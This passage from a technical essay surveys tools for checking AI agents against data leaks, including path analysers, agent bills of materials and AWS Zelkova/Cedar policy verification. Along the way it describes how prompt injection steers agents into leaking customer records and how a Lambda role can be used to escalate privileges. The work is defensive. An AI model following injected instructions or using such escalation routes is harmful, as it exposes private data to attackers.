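Some of Spera's further results are wrong, and two of the errors would matter to anyone building a checker. One concerns how hard it is to decide whether a given set B is a minimal unsafe set. Both papers state that this problem is coNP-complete, which would mean that no fast method exists unless P = NP, a famous conjecture that most computer scientists have long doubted. But there is a simple fast method:

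1. Compute cl(B) and confirm that it contains a forbidden fact.
2. For each member b of B, compute the closure of B without b and confirm that it contains none.

Testing the removals one at a time is enough because every smaller subset of B lies inside one of the sets from step 2, and any subset of a safe set is safe. The method takes |B| + 1 closure computations, where |B| is the number of members in B, so the shop's three-member minimal set takes four. The same one-at-a-time test can also quickly check whether a set is a minimal transversal (a set that includes at least one member of every group in a list, but would miss a group if any member were removed), which is the problem that Spera's proof starts from and assumes is hard.

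Listing *all* the minimal unsafe sets can take a very long time, because there may be exponentially many. If a leak needs 20 conditions and either of two different tools can supply each one, there are 2²⁰, or about a million, minimal sets. The trifecta has only three conditions, so the number stays manageable.

The other error concerns submodularity, the mathematical name for diminishing returns. Spera states that adding a capability to a larger set never enlarges the closure by more than adding it to a smaller one. The paper's own example with u₁, u₂ and f contradicts this. Adding u₂ to the empty set adds one fact, u₂ itself, while adding it to {u₁} adds two, u₂ and f. Returns increase in this way whenever a rule needs two conditions and one is already present.

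Spera uses submodularity to derive a guarantee that the greedy method, which picks the capability that adds the most at each step, should reach at least 63% of the best possible result. Suppose u₁ and u₂ together unlock 100 further facts, while x and y each unlock one. With two picks allowed, the greedy method takes x and y, because each adds two facts (itself and the one it unlocks), while u₁ or u₂ alone adds only itself. It gains 4 new facts out of a possible 102, far below the guaranteed 63%. A security team that used this method to look for the most dangerous additions to an agent could miss the pairs that combination rules are meant to find.

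Spera also makes a smaller error about what he calls the safe audit surface, a map of the capabilities an agent could safely gain. According to one lemma, every safe addition is the last missing condition of some rule, but a clock tool that no rule mentions is safe to add and doesn't complete any rule. None of these errors affects the closure computation or the theorem about unions, both of which are easy to verify by hand.

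### An earlier trial on Android phones

Combination rules were tried on phone apps long before anyone applied them to AI agents. *On Lightweight Mobile Phone Application Certification*, a 2009 paper by William Enck, Machigar Ongtang and Patrick McDaniel, introduced Kirin, a security service for Android phones. Every Android app came with a manifest, a file listing the permissions it requested. When a user tried to install an app, Kirin checked the manifest against nine rules, most of which named permissions that an app must not hold together.

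| Permissions together | Misuse the rule was meant to prevent |
|---|---|
| Read the phone's state, record audio, use the internet | Recording calls and sending them away |
| Read the location, use the internet, start when the phone starts | Tracking the phone's owner |
| Send text messages, write to the message store | Sending messages and hiding the evidence |
| Install shortcuts, remove shortcuts | Replacing a trusted app's shortcut with a link to a fake |

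The location rule had two versions, one for precise positions and one for approximate positions. Kirin also had a rule that checked only one setting and rejected any app that asked for permission to turn on debugging for other apps.

Enck, Ongtang and McDaniel tested the rules on 311 of the most popular apps in the official Android Market. The rules flagged ten apps, or 3.2% of the sample. The researchers found that five of these had dangerous functions and that users should install them only with extreme caution. The other five asked for dangerous permissions but, judging by their descriptions, had a reasonable need for them. If only the first five count as correct findings, the precision was 50%. They could not measure recall because nobody knew how many of the other 301 apps were harmful.

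That is a light workload for a reviewer compared with munio, which reported toxic flows on 46% of servers, partly because Kirin's rules were narrow. Many legitimate apps need both the microphone and the internet, for example to make voice calls. The first rule in the table also required access to the phone's state, which lets an app detect when a call begins, so it did not flag apps that had no way to time a recording. Similarly, the location rule did not flag a map app that runs only when the user opens it.

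A rule for agents could be narrowed in the same way. It could flag an agent with the full trifecta only if strangers can write to the agent without an invitation, or if nobody approves its outgoing messages. The shop's agent would still match, but an agent that reads documents from two known suppliers would not. Attackers could still hack one of those suppliers, so the narrower rule would miss some real attacks.

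Kirin's input was also more reliable than that of an agent configuration checker. Android had a fixed list of permissions and the operating system enforced them, so an app that had not requested the microphone could not normally record audio. An agent's capability labels often come from a classifier applied to a tool's description, and nothing stops a mislabelled tool from doing more than its label indicates.

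Even on Android, Kirin's rules covered only one app at a time. An app with microphone access could send a recording to another app with internet access, and each would pass the check separately. Catching this would have required checking the permissions of all installed apps together and knowing which of them could exchange data.

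## Tracing paths through agents, tools and shared memory

The two-agent version of the shop fails a combination rule because the agents together have every capability needed for a leak. Whether they can leak a customer's record also depends on which agent goes first. If the records agent goes first, it can hand the ticket and the customer's record to the parcel agent, which can put both into a web address. If the parcel agent goes first, it hands over only the ticket's parcel number and some web pages, and the customer's record stays with the records agent, which cannot send anything.

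A flow path is a chain of steps through which data can travel. Each step may be a tool result, a message between agents, or a note that one agent saves and another reads. A leak requires an agent that receives untrusted text through one flow path and private data through another, and that can use an outbound channel.

| Arrangement | What can reach the agent with `http_get` | Leak possible |
|---|---|---|
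| Records agent hands over to parcel agent | Ticket text, web pages and customer records | Yes |
| Parcel agent hands over to records agent | Parcel numbers and web pages | No |
| The same, but both agents use one saved memory | Also customer records from earlier conversations | Yes |

A combination rule that pools the two agents' labels reports a leak in all three cases.

### From source code to three graphs

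*AGENTFLOW* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that searches agents' source code for paths. Some of the same researchers also built TaintAWI, the scanner for GitHub workflows. Most of the agents in the study use a framework, a library that runs the loop and lets the programmer declare agents, tools and memory. Frameworks hide paths from ordinary code analysers because a line such as `tools=[send_email]` only puts a function in a list. The framework calls that function later, when the model outputs a call to it.

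AgentFlow first translates the code into simple facts, such as "this agent may call that tool". It recognises 143 constructs from five Python frameworks, including LangGraph, CrewAI and OpenAI's Agents SDK. It also traces each name back to its definition, because the approval setting for `send_email` may be many lines away from the agent that uses the tool.

AgentFlow uses these facts to build three graphs with the same nodes: agents, prompts, models, tools, memories and guards. A guard is a control on a path, such as human approval or input validation.

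- The component graph links each agent to its prompt, model, tools and memory.
- The control-flow graph shows what can run next. An edge leads from an agent to each tool it may call and each agent it may hand over to. If a guard protects the tool, the route goes from the agent to the guard and then to the tool.
- The data-flow graph shows where information can travel: from prompts to agents, from agents to tools and back, between agents, and in and out of memory.

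Wang and colleagues call the three together an agent dependency graph.

### A search agent and an e-mail agent

In their example, a research agent can search the web and an operations agent can send e-mail. A user asks the system to search for recent updates and notify Alice.

| In the code | What AgentFlow adds to the graphs |
|---|---|
| The research agent lists `web_search` as a tool | A control edge to the tool, and data edges to it and back |
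| The research agent lists a handoff to the operations agent | A control edge and a message edge between the agents |
| The operations agent lists `send_email` as a tool | A control edge to the tool, and data edges to it and back |
| `send_email` always requires approval | A guard between the operations agent and the tool |
| The run uses a saved session | A memory through which the agents can share information |

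AgentFlow then runs what its makers call a prompt-to-tool query. It reports a prompt p, an agent a and a sensitive tool c if

1. data can flow from p to a, through any number of other nodes,
2. control can pass from a to c, and
3. a can fill in the arguments of c.

Let p be the research agent's prompt. The first condition holds for both agents, because information from the prompt can reach the operations agent through the handoff. The second also holds for both, because the research agent can hand over to the operations agent, which can call `send_email`. Only the operations agent meets the third, because the research agent never writes an e-mail itself. The query therefore reports the research agent's prompt, the operations agent and `send_email`.

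The checker reports this path despite the approval requirement, because the route from the operations agent to `send_email` still exists, although it passes through the guard. To find only unapproved paths, the checker can delete the guard nodes and search again, and `send_email` is then unreachable. This second search doesn't show whether people approve messages carefully enough to justify ignoring the guarded paths.

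The query also covers less than the trifecta. It doesn't check for private data, and neither agent in the example has a tool for reading it. The query starts from prompts, but the hostile text in such a program would more likely come from a web page that `web_search` returns. The data-flow graph contains that route too, so a trifecta query could use the same graph. It would look for an agent that both untrusted content and private data can reach, and that can fill in the arguments of an outbound tool.

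Taken literally, the three conditions hold for nearly any agent with a prompt and a sensitive tool, so the number of reports depends heavily on which prompts count as sources and which tools count as sensitive.

### Results on 5,399 programs

Wang and colleagues ran AgentFlow on 5,399 agent projects from GitHub. It flagged 238 of them (4.4%), with 4,357 separate findings. In 129 of the flagged projects, the tool at the end of the path could send data externally. The median project took 14 seconds to analyze.

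Two of the researchers checked 100 of the findings against the source code and judged 73 correct. In 25 of the 27 wrong ones, the path was real but AgentFlow's capability label overstated the tool's danger. Thirteen of these tools read local files without changing or deleting them, seven ran read-only database queries, and five were restricted calculators. So at least 98 of the 100 findings contained a valid path.

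Some of those 25 errors might not be errors when checking for data theft, because a tool that only reads files or database records can supply the private data in a trifecta. A checker looking for leaks would need to keep the file and database tools under a different label and could safely drop only the calculators.

Another scanner from the same research group made fewer mistakes. In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) used it to search 6,549 repositories for agents that could repeat costly steps without an effective limit, and confirmed 68 of its 74 findings (92%). One likely reason is that a missing limit is visible in the program's structure, whereas a tool's potential for harm often is not.

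Wang and colleagues also looked for missed problems by inspecting 100 agents that had privileged tools but in which AgentFlow had reported no problems. Nine had a real prompt-to-tool risk. AgentFlow missed these mostly because the programmers had written their own wrappers around commands or tools, or had attached tools while the program was running.

Recall cannot be computed from the two samples as 73 / (73 + 9) = 89%, because they come from groups of different sizes and the study does not give the size of the second group. Suppose AgentFlow had flagged 1,000 agents, 730 of them correctly. If 2,000 other agents had privileged tools, a 9% miss rate would mean 180 missed risks and a recall of 80%. With 20,000 such agents, there would be 1,800 missed risks and recall would fall to 29%. The samples also count different things, because one agent can have many findings. Neither sample would include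 an agent whose dangerous tool nobody had recognised as privileged.

### Agent bills of materials

The component graph can also serve as an agent bill of materials. A software bill of materials lists the packages in a program, so that a company can quickly find out whether it uses one with a newly discovered flaw. An agent bill of materials would also list prompts, models, tools, memories and the links between them. Dutta and Moharir (2026), in *AgentRiskBOM*, propose adding the scope of each credential, the approval gates and the communication between agents, and tried their format on 13 open-source agents. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (2026) combines such a list with records of what the agent did while running. These records help to reconstruct an attack but are not available before deployment. There was no agreed standard for agent bills of materials in April 2026, according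 to *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026).

The links matter most for a capability check, because a list of two agents, a database tool and a web tool does not show whether one agent holds both tools. Wang and colleagues compared AgentFlow with three existing generators on 100 projects. Trusera's generator produced 3,615 entries, mostly models and software packages, with no agents and no links. Cisco's produced 141 entries and 22 links. AgentFlow produced 2,295 entries and 1,008 links, of which 403 connected an agent to a tool and only 50 connected two agents.

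Those 50 links can involve at most 100 of the 784 agents that AgentFlow listed, so at least 684 had no recorded link to another agent. AgentFlow may have missed some links. Paths between agents are important in a minority of programs.

### The same command in three tools

Paths also run through the code inside a tool. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) illustrates this with three tools that all run a command on the computer. The first runs the command the model supplies. The second replaces the model's text with a fixed command. The third checks the model's text against a list of permitted commands before running it. All three could be labelled "runs commands", but an attacker can't choose the command in the second and can choose only from the permitted list in the third.

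Cui's program, AgentSecGraph, works backwards through the code from each sensitive operation to check whether text from the agent can influence it, and records possible guards along the way. Of the 23,866 sensitive operations it found in 67 repositories of agent software, it traced 9,821 (41%) back to an input and detected a possible guard for 3,075 (13%).

The other 59% are not necessarily safe. AgentSecGraph found an input for 84% of the operations that write files but for only 11% of calls to external tools. The difference is probably due to the difficulty of following data into an external tool, since AgentSecGraph mostly traces data within a small part of the program. It recovered no evidence about the privileges the operations run with. Its results may show a database query with a complete path and a guard, but not which tables the query can read.

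Cui then reproduced 22 of the behaviours in controlled tests or by close examination of the code. One was a confirmed vulnerability, and another was still awaiting a decision. The other 20 did not qualify as vulnerabilities under the tested conditions because of guards or limits on how people use the program. It would therefore be misleading to treat every path to a powerful operation as a vulnerability. The 22 cases were not a random sample, so they cannot be used to estimate the proportion of operations that are dangerous.

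AgentSecGraph's guard evidence shows only that a check is present in the code, not that the check works. A list of permitted commands that includes `curl` would count as a guard, even though an attacker could still use `curl` to send data out.

### When one agent holds all the tools

Nobody can know before deployment which tools a model will call, in what order or with what arguments. Path analysers therefore over-approximate, meaning they include everything the program permits, even if it may never happen. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) explicitly assumes that once any tool's output has entered the model's context, every tool the model can reach may read that output.

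For a single agent that chooses freely among its tools, path analysis is therefore equivalent to a combination rule. In the original shop, the ticket's text and the customer's record both enter the context from which the model writes the arguments of `http_get`. This creates a path from `read_ticket` to `http_get` and another from `lookup_customer` to `http_get`, and the same would be true of any other tools in their place. If the agent has all three labels, the paths exist, so drawing the graph adds nothing to the finding.

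The assumption is pessimistic. One of the ten tool chains that Zhao and colleagues attacked never leaked anything, because the model never took the last step. But it is hard to replace the assumption with something more precise. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) argues that traditional taint analysis does not carry over directly to agents, because a model may summarise a hostile text, rephrase it or let it influence the choice of the next tool. It would also be unwise to exclude a path because the model has never used it, since an attacker may be the first to try it.

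Over-approximation is guaranteed to include every path only if the graph is complete. The nine risks that AgentFlow missed came from code it had not fully analyzed, and no assumption about the model could have recovered them.

Path analysis can still add something for a single agent when data travels between tools without passing through the model. Santra and colleagues give an example with two tools. `get_news` reads an access token for a news service and stores it in a dictionary that all the tools share. `sync_prefs` is meant to save the user's preferences, and it sends that whole dictionary to a server. Their program, ACaM, traces the leak in three steps:

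1. The shared dictionary starts with the label "internal".
2. `get_news` writes the token into it, so ACaM raises the label to "secret".
3. `sync_prefs` reads the dictionary and sends it out, so ACaM reports a path from the token to the preferences server.

The token leaks whenever the agent uses the two tools in this order, even without an attacker. The tools' descriptions mention only headlines and preferences, so a classifier that reads descriptions would probably miss the leak.

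The same method can also remove false alarms. ACaM assumes that a secret reaches the model only if a tool returns it. The shop's `lookup_customer` uses a database token but returns only the customer's record, so a hostile ticket cannot make the model reveal the token through this tool. The label "reads secrets" alone would not distinguish the token from the record.

ACaM tracks secrets and untrusted text separately. On a single scale from public to secret, text from a web page would be labelled "public". If a tool combined that text with a secret, the result would be labelled "secret", and the analysis would no longer show that part of it was untrusted.

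Santra and colleagues planted leaks in 14 versions of real agents and scored how much of each path a method recovered. ACaM scored 0.98 out of 1, compared with 0.90 for the best results from language models working alone. The models could usually identify the secret and the place where it left the program, but 40% of the time they failed to give the full chain of steps between them, while ACaM failed 7% of the time.

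On 43 unmodified agents, ACaM reported 1,692 paths for indirect prompt injection, about 39 per agent. This follows almost directly from the assumption, since any tool that fetches outside text opens a path to the model. The list is too long to help much with setting priorities. The 123 most severe paths, which involve running code or exposing credentials, are more useful, and the researchers confirmed by hand that all of them exist in the code. They also built exploits for ten of the findings. All ten worked against a small model with little safety training, and against Claude Haiku 4.5 after the researchers phrased the attacks more subtly. They did not test stronger models. Two of the exploits do not depend on the model, because the agent runs the attacker's code while loading a file at startup.

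### Handoffs that carry less

When a program divides its tools among several agents, path analysis can clear arrangements that a combination rule would flag, as in the shop with the parcel agent first. A one-way handoff protects the later agent's data because nothing flows back, but hostile text can still reach that agent. In OpenAI's Agents SDK, the agent that takes over sees the entire previous conversation unless the programmer adds a filter. In the e-mail example, the operations agent would therefore read any instructions the research agent had picked up from a web page.

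A checker also has to confirm that the handoff goes only one way. If one agent calls another as a tool, the second agent's answer returns to the first. A shared session can also carry information back if the first agent reads it during the next conversation.

A handoff between agents can block hostile text only if it is too narrow to carry an instruction. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) proposes a quarantined agent that reads untrusted material and a privileged agent that chooses actions. The quarantined agent may pass on only certain types of data, never free text. *L3M* (2026) gives a small example in which an agent has to sort bug reports that anyone can write. A separate agent with no access to files or the network reads the reports instead, and it can answer one question about each report with only one of three fixed words.

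Each answer gives the writer of the report at most log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits of influence over the agent that acts. The writer can cause a wrong answer, and so perhaps a wrongly sorted report, but cannot tell the agent to fetch a file. This holds only if timing and failures reveal nothing more and the acting agent has no other way to read the report. A path analyser can check the second condition by looking for another route from the report to the agent. It also has to confirm that the program, not just the prompt, restricts answers to the three allowed words.

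### Fixed workflows

Order matters when the programmer sets it instead of leaving it to the model. Suppose the shop replaces its free-running agent with a fixed sequence that reads the ticket, fetches the parcel's status, looks up the customer and drafts a reply. The only step that can contact the web now finishes before the customer record enters the context. A combination rule still flags the agent because it has all three labels, but a path analyser can clear the finding because no route leads from `lookup_customer` back to `http_get`. If a programmer later adds a "try again" edge from the draft to the web step, that route exists and the analyser reports the finding again.

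In *Agentproof*, Xavier, Jolly and colleagues (2026) check workflows of this kind with a program that extracts the steps and permitted transitions from four frameworks. One check looks for paths that reach a sensitive tool without passing a human reviewer. The program deletes all the human steps and searches from the start, and any sensitive tool it can still reach has an unreviewed path. The program prints that path to show developers where the gap is.

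Agentproof can also test rules about order, such as requiring a person to review each e-mail draft before the next one is written. It turns the rule into a small state machine, then explores every combination of a workflow step and a machine state. If any combination breaks the rule, so does some path through the workflow. With |V| steps and |Q| states, there are at most |V| × |Q| combinations, so the search is fast. The simpler structural checks took about a tenth of a second on a workflow with 5,000 steps.

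The rule language can't directly express the rule the shop needs, "after a customer lookup, never a web request". It can express "never a lookup, or never a web request", which flags any path that contains both. That rule would also flag the safe order, a web request followed by a lookup, but it would clear a workflow that sends each ticket down one of two separate branches.

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows that they had written themselves, partly to contain known mistakes. Five had structural defects, such as a step with no way out, and ten had no human step, though some low-risk workflows do not need one. The published precision of the human-step check is 75%, with one false positive, which implies that only three of the ten findings were clearly correct, one was wrong and six were debatable. Because the workflows were built for the test, these figures do not show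 how common the problems are in practice.

Agentproof also over-approximates. It treats every branch of a workflow as possible, including some that the code's conditions rule out, and Xavier and colleagues did not measure how many false alarms this causes. Agentproof can also miss real problems, because for LangGraph it identifies a human step by the word "human" in its name. An automated step called `human_summary` could presumably pass as a reviewer. The same rule overlooks reviewer steps with other names.

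Fixed workflows seem to be common in companies. *Measuring Agents in Production* (2025) found them in 16 of 20 case studies, although the sample is small and the study is a year old. In one of these workflows, an agent always checks insurance coverage, then medical necessity, then risks, but works freely within each step. A path analyser has to assume that the model can use a step's tools in any order. The shop's workflow is therefore safe only if the lookup step has no access to `http_get`, and the program has to enforce this by giving each step its own list of tools.

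## What cloud permission analysers can prove

A path through an agent's tools reaches private data only if the last tool's credential grants access to that data. In a cloud account, identity and access management (IAM) controls this access by checking whether an identity, such as an employee or a program, may perform an action on a resource, such as a stored file. An IAM policy specifies who may do what to which resource, and under what conditions. Because policies have an exact meaning, a program can analyse every possible request, including requests that nobody has made yet.

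On AWS, a request succeeds only if at least one "allow" statement matches it and no "deny" statement does. The order of the statements makes no difference. Suppose the shop keeps its customer records in a bucket, a storage area in Amazon's S3 service. The following policy, adapted from an example in AWS's *Access Control Verification for Everyone* (2020), lets one account read the records, but only from the shop's own network:

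```json
[
  { "Effect": "Allow",
    "Principal": { "AWS": "111122223333" },
    "Action": "s3:GetObject",
    "Resource": "arn:aws:s3:::shop-records/*" },
  { "Effect": "Deny",
    "Principal": "*",
    "Action": "*",
    "Resource": "arn:aws:s3:::shop-records/*",
    "Condition": {
      "StringNotEquals": { "aws:SourceVpc": "vpc-shop" } } }
]
```

### Turning a policy into a formula

Backes, Bolignano and colleagues (2018), in *Semantic-based Automated Reasoning for AWS Access Policies using SMT*, describe Zelkova, the program AWS uses to analyse such policies. Zelkova translates a policy into a logical formula. For the shop's bucket, let p be the account that sends the request, a the action, r the file and n the network:

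Allow = (p = 111122223333) and (a = GetObject) and (r starts with "shop-records/")

Deny = (r starts with "shop-records/") and (n ≠ vpc-shop)

Granted = Allow and not Deny

To find out whether anyone can read a record from outside the shop's network, Zelkova adds the condition n ≠ vpc-shop and gives the result to an SMT solver. This is a program that either finds values that make a formula true or proves that no such values exist. Here the proof is short:

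1. Granted requires Allow, so the file must be in `shop-records`.
2. Granted also requires Deny to be false. For a file in `shop-records`, that means n = vpc-shop.
3. The question assumed n ≠ vpc-shop, so no request fits.

The result holds for every account, file name and network. Nobody could establish this by testing requests one at a time, because there are 10¹² possible AWS account numbers and 2¹²⁸ possible IPv6 addresses.

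If a colleague then narrows the deny statement to `shop-records/customers/*`, the formula has a solution, such as a request from a café's network for `shop-records/exports/all-customers.csv`. Someone who stole a key to the shop's account could read that file from anywhere. The 2018 version of Zelkova would have reported that the check failed without showing the offending request, a feature its developers listed as future work.

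Simpler checkers search the policy's text for warning signs, such as an asterisk where the account should be. Backes and colleagues use two message queue policies to show why this is unreliable. Both let anyone send a message on condition that it comes from one named source. The second policy adds the prefix `ForAllValues` to the condition, which makes the condition true even for a request that names no source, so anyone on the internet can send messages to that queue. If an agent reads its tasks from the queue, strangers can send it tasks.

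Zelkova can also compare two policies, so a security team can write its requirement as a policy and check whether the real policy ever permits more. In one example, a university's first policy lets students read an exam and lets teaching assistants read the exam and the answers. The second lets everyone read the whole folder, except that students cannot read the answers. Zelkova proves that the second policy permits everything the first does. The second also permits more, because it opens the folder to the entire internet, and anyone not identified as a student can read even the answers.

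Asterisks in file names make these questions PSPACE-complete, so no known method solves all of them quickly. Real policies are usually easy, though. Zelkova answered 99% of a million randomly chosen questions within 160 milliseconds. It runs three solvers at once and takes the first answer. If all three time out, or the policy contains something Zelkova cannot translate, it returns "unknown", which a careful checker has to treat as possible access.

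In 2018, AWS services called Zelkova between a few million and tens of millions of times a day. Neha Rungta of AWS reported in *A Billion SMT Queries a Day* (2022) that solver queries had grown from a thousand a day to a billion in five years. The two figures are not directly comparable because one query to Zelkova can start several solvers. Still, this kind of analysis is clearly fast enough to run every time an agent's permissions change.

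### From proofs to a short list of findings

A solver checks only the properties that someone specifies. *Stratified Abstraction of Access Control Policies* (Backes, Berrueco and colleagues, 2020) explains that customers had to know which property mattered to them, express it in Zelkova's terms and interpret the result. AWS therefore changed the question from "is this policy correct?" to "who has access?" in IAM Access Analyzer, launched in December 2019.

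One example policy has three statements. The first allows requests from networks A and B, the second allows requests from company 2, and the third denies requests from network B unless they come from company 1. The combined effect is hard to see from the statements.

| | Company 1 | Company 2 | Any other company |
|---|---|---|---|
| Network A | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Network B | Allowed | Denied | Denied |
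| Any other network | Denied | Allowed | Denied |

Access Analyzer summarises the five allowed cells in three findings: network A has access, company 2 has access, and company 1 has access from network B. It starts with the broadest statement, "anyone from anywhere", and uses Zelkova to check whether that covers an allowed request that no narrower statement covers. If so, the statement becomes a finding; otherwise, Access Analyzer splits it into narrower statements and checks again. This example takes six checks, and Access Analyzer never has to look at the companies within network A separately.

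The list of findings is complete, so a customer who accepts each finding has accepted everything the policy permits. But a finding can be slightly too broad. For example, "Company 2 has access" includes requests from network B, even though the policy denies them. AWS allows this imprecision to keep the list shorter.

The researchers drew 1,387 policies at random from those in use and set aside the 88% with fewer than ten possible findings. For 64% of the remaining 165, Access Analyzer produced at most a fifth of the possible findings. The method therefore summarises well, but its lists may still be too long to read, because a fifth of a thousand possible findings is 200. The average time per finding was under 0.43 seconds for every policy but one.

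### True findings about intended access

If Access Analyzer reports that a delivery company can read the shop's parcel list, the owner might call it a false alarm because the shop may have arranged that access, but the finding is still correct. A false proof would be much worse, because the analyser would report that no outsider can read a file when one can. This could happen if Zelkova mistranslated one of AWS's rules. A more likely cause is a question that is too narrow, for example one that covers the bucket's policy but not a second copy of the data elsewhere.

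A solver cannot determine whether access is intended, so Access Analyzer leaves that decision to the customer. The summary of *Access Control Verification for Everyone* describes this as the reverse of ordinary verification, because the service first finds what is true of a policy and customers then identify which of those facts they intended. Customers can archive findings about intended access. For unintended access, the service links to the policy that grants it, runs again after the policy is edited, and marks the finding as resolved once the access is gone.

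Little has been published on how customers respond to findings. The 2020 paper measures speed and the number of findings, but not how many people archive, repair or archive by mistake. The 2018 paper describes an auditing system for AWS's own accounts that opens a ticket for each violation, assigns it to the resource's owner and closes it after the repair, but the paper gives no rates for this process. Archiving also carries a risk when agents are involved. If the delivery company later lets an agent use its account, that agent can read the parcel list too, and the shop's archived finding will look the same as before.

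The S3 setting Block Public Access rejects policies that would make a bucket public. AWS has turned it on by default for new buckets since April 2023, so customers who want a public bucket must turn it off. The setting needs a definition of "public" that works without any information about the customer. *Projective Model Counting for IP Addresses in Access Control* (D'Antoni, 2024) explains the definition AWS chose. A policy counts as public if it grants access to anyone other than the trusted entities it names, such as particular accounts, users or networks. A program extracts those entities, and Zelkova checks whether the policy grants access to anyone else.

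This definition of public access works badly for internet addresses. An office may use a range of several hundred addresses, and if each one counts as a separate trusted entity, a sensible policy can look public. But a range that covers half the internet is public, so the analysis has to consider how many addresses a policy lets in. The owner of a public website has to switch the protection off, which takes a moment, but the protection blocks accidental public access to a bucket before any data leaks.

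### Roles that lead to other roles

A proof about one bucket can be correct and still miss a way in. Suppose the shop's agent runs with a cloud role called `support`, which cannot read the customer records. Another role, `reports`, can. The `support` role may also create small programs in AWS's Lambda service and assign them any role in the account. An attacker who steers the agent can then:

1. create a program that copies the customer records,
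2. assign it the `reports` role, and
3. run it and read the output.

A list of the identities that can read the records would correctly include only `reports`. The danger is that `support` can use `reports`. Security engineers call it privilege escalation when an identity uses its permissions to gain others it was not supposed to have. A simpler form is role assumption, in which AWS lets one identity switch directly to another role.

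Analysers find such routes by building a permission graph, whose edges show which identity, agent or tool can reach which resource or other identity. Principal Mapper (PMapper), an open-source program from the security company NCC Group, does this for AWS. Each user and role is a node, and an edge from one to another means that the first can obtain the second's permissions. PMapper would draw an edge from `support` to `reports`, and a search along the edges would show that the agent can reach the customer records. People also use PMapper to find ordinary identities that can make themselves administrators.

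BloodHound, which Andy Robbins, Rohan Vazarkar and Will Schroeder released in 2016, applied the same idea to company networks that use Microsoft's Active Directory to manage users and computers. Its edges include group membership, control over a computer and an administrator's open session on a computer. In a typical path, an ordinary employee controls a computer where an administrator is logged in, and could steal the administrator's credentials from it. Sessions change from hour to hour, so a path found in the morning may be gone by the afternoon, and new ones may have opened.

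The graph search is exact, but the edges may be wrong or missing. Somebody has to know that creating a Lambda program and assigning it a role amounts to taking over the role, and write a rule for it. A new cloud service that can run code may add a route that no rule covers yet. *Cloud Resource Protection via Automated Security Property Reasoning*, published by Amazon, criticises third-party tools for judging policies by patterns in their text, which leads to false alarms and missed problems. Amazon has an interest in recommending its own tool, Zelkova, but the queue example supports the criticism. A solver can establish each edge reliably, and a graph search can then join the edges.

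### Why no program can answer the general question

PMapper examines permissions as they are now. It is harder to determine whether an identity could *ever* gain a permission, given everything that people and programs might do later. *Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) studies this question using a table with a row for each identity, a column for each resource and permissions in the cells. Commands of the form "if these permissions are present, add or remove those" change the table, and may also create rows and columns. A system is safe for a given permission if no sequence of commands can put that permission into a cell where it was absent.

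"Protection in Operating Systems" proved that whether a system's commands could ever grant a forbidden permission is undecidable, meaning no program can answer the question correctly for every system. The proof builds a table of permissions that imitates a Turing machine, a simple model of a computer that can carry out any computation. Each square of the machine's tape becomes an identity, permissions represent the symbols on the tape, and each command carries out one step. A final command grants the forbidden permission when the machine stops. A program that could always answer the question could therefore determine whether any given computation stops, which Alan Turing had proved impossible in 1936.

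The construction needs an unlimited supply of new identities. If commands cannot create anything, the number of possible tables is finite, and a program could search them all, although this might take far too long.

Restricting the commands can make the problem easy even when identities can create others. In the take-grant model, a "take" edge lets one identity copy another's permissions, and a "grant" edge lets it give another its own. Richard Lipton and Lawrence Snyder showed in 1977 how to decide whether an identity can ever obtain a permission, in time proportional to the size of the graph. If every node is an active identity, an identity can obtain the permission if and only if a chain of take and grant edges connects it to one that already holds the permission. The direction of the edges does not matter, because the identities can help one another pass permissions along.

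That last condition assumes that everyone on the chain cooperates, which is too pessimistic when one agent is hijacked and the others on the chain are honest. IAM also has conditions on networks, times and file names that the take-grant model lacks. Analysers avoid undecidability by checking a snapshot of the permissions and repeating the check after each change. This works best if the agent cannot change those permissions. Analysers should therefore assume that an agent allowed to create roles or edit policies can obtain whatever those roles and policies could grant.

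### What carries over to agents

| Question about an agent | Can an analyser prove the answer? | What the proof depends on |
|---|---|---|
| Which stored data can it read? | Yes | All the policies that apply, and the roles it can take over |
| Which hosts can it contact? | Often | Network rules that something enforces |
| Which tool calls will a gateway permit? | Yes | Every call going through the gateway |
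| Who can write to the places it reads from? | Often | Formal permissions on those places |
| Is the text it reads trustworthy? | No | |
| Will the model follow a hostile instruction? | No | |

Companies other than cloud providers can also produce the first kind of proof. *How Stedi Uses Automated Reasoning for Access Control Policy Verification* (Jeon, Conijn and Tcholakov, 2023) describes a software company that had to show that its own employees could never read customers' data. The company built its own translation of AWS policies for Z3, a solver from Microsoft. The same method would work for an agent's role, but it would not cover ambient credentials, such as an engineer's login that the agent finds on a laptop.

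*Reachability Analysis for AWS-based Networks* (Backes) describes Tiros, a program that translates AWS network settings into logic and uses automated provers to check them against a customer's requirements. Such a proof assumes that the network behaves as AWS documents it, but the Code Interpreter's "Sandbox" setting did not behave as documented.

Cloud permission analysers can only partly check whether an agent is exposed to untrusted content. Zelkova can prove that only employees can write to a bucket, which rules out strangers adding files directly. But an employee may save a customer's e-mail in that bucket, and permissions don't record who wrote it.

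The model's behaviour is the last unknown, but a proof doesn't need to predict it if it covers everything the model might do. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) treat the model as a source of arbitrary actions and prove that the software around it enforces a given limit whatever the model outputs. This works only for limits that can be stated in terms of actions, their arguments and the state of the system, such as "never contact a host outside this list", so it can't cover a limit like "never send a misleading reply".

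### Cedar policies in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore

AWS now applies this approach to agents' tools. In its agent service, Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, a gateway checks each tool call against policies written in Cedar, an open-source policy language that AWS designed. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* advises companies to treat the model as an untrusted actor. The gateway blocks any call that no policy permits, and a "forbid" rule overrides any "permit" rule, much as in IAM.

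Such a policy could have protected Dana Reyes, the customer whose record the attacker stole from the shop. Suppose customers have to log in before filing a ticket, and the agent handles each ticket under that customer's verified identity:

```text
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"lookup_customer",
  resource
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("customer_id") &&
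  context.input.customerId == principal.getTag("customer_id")
};
```

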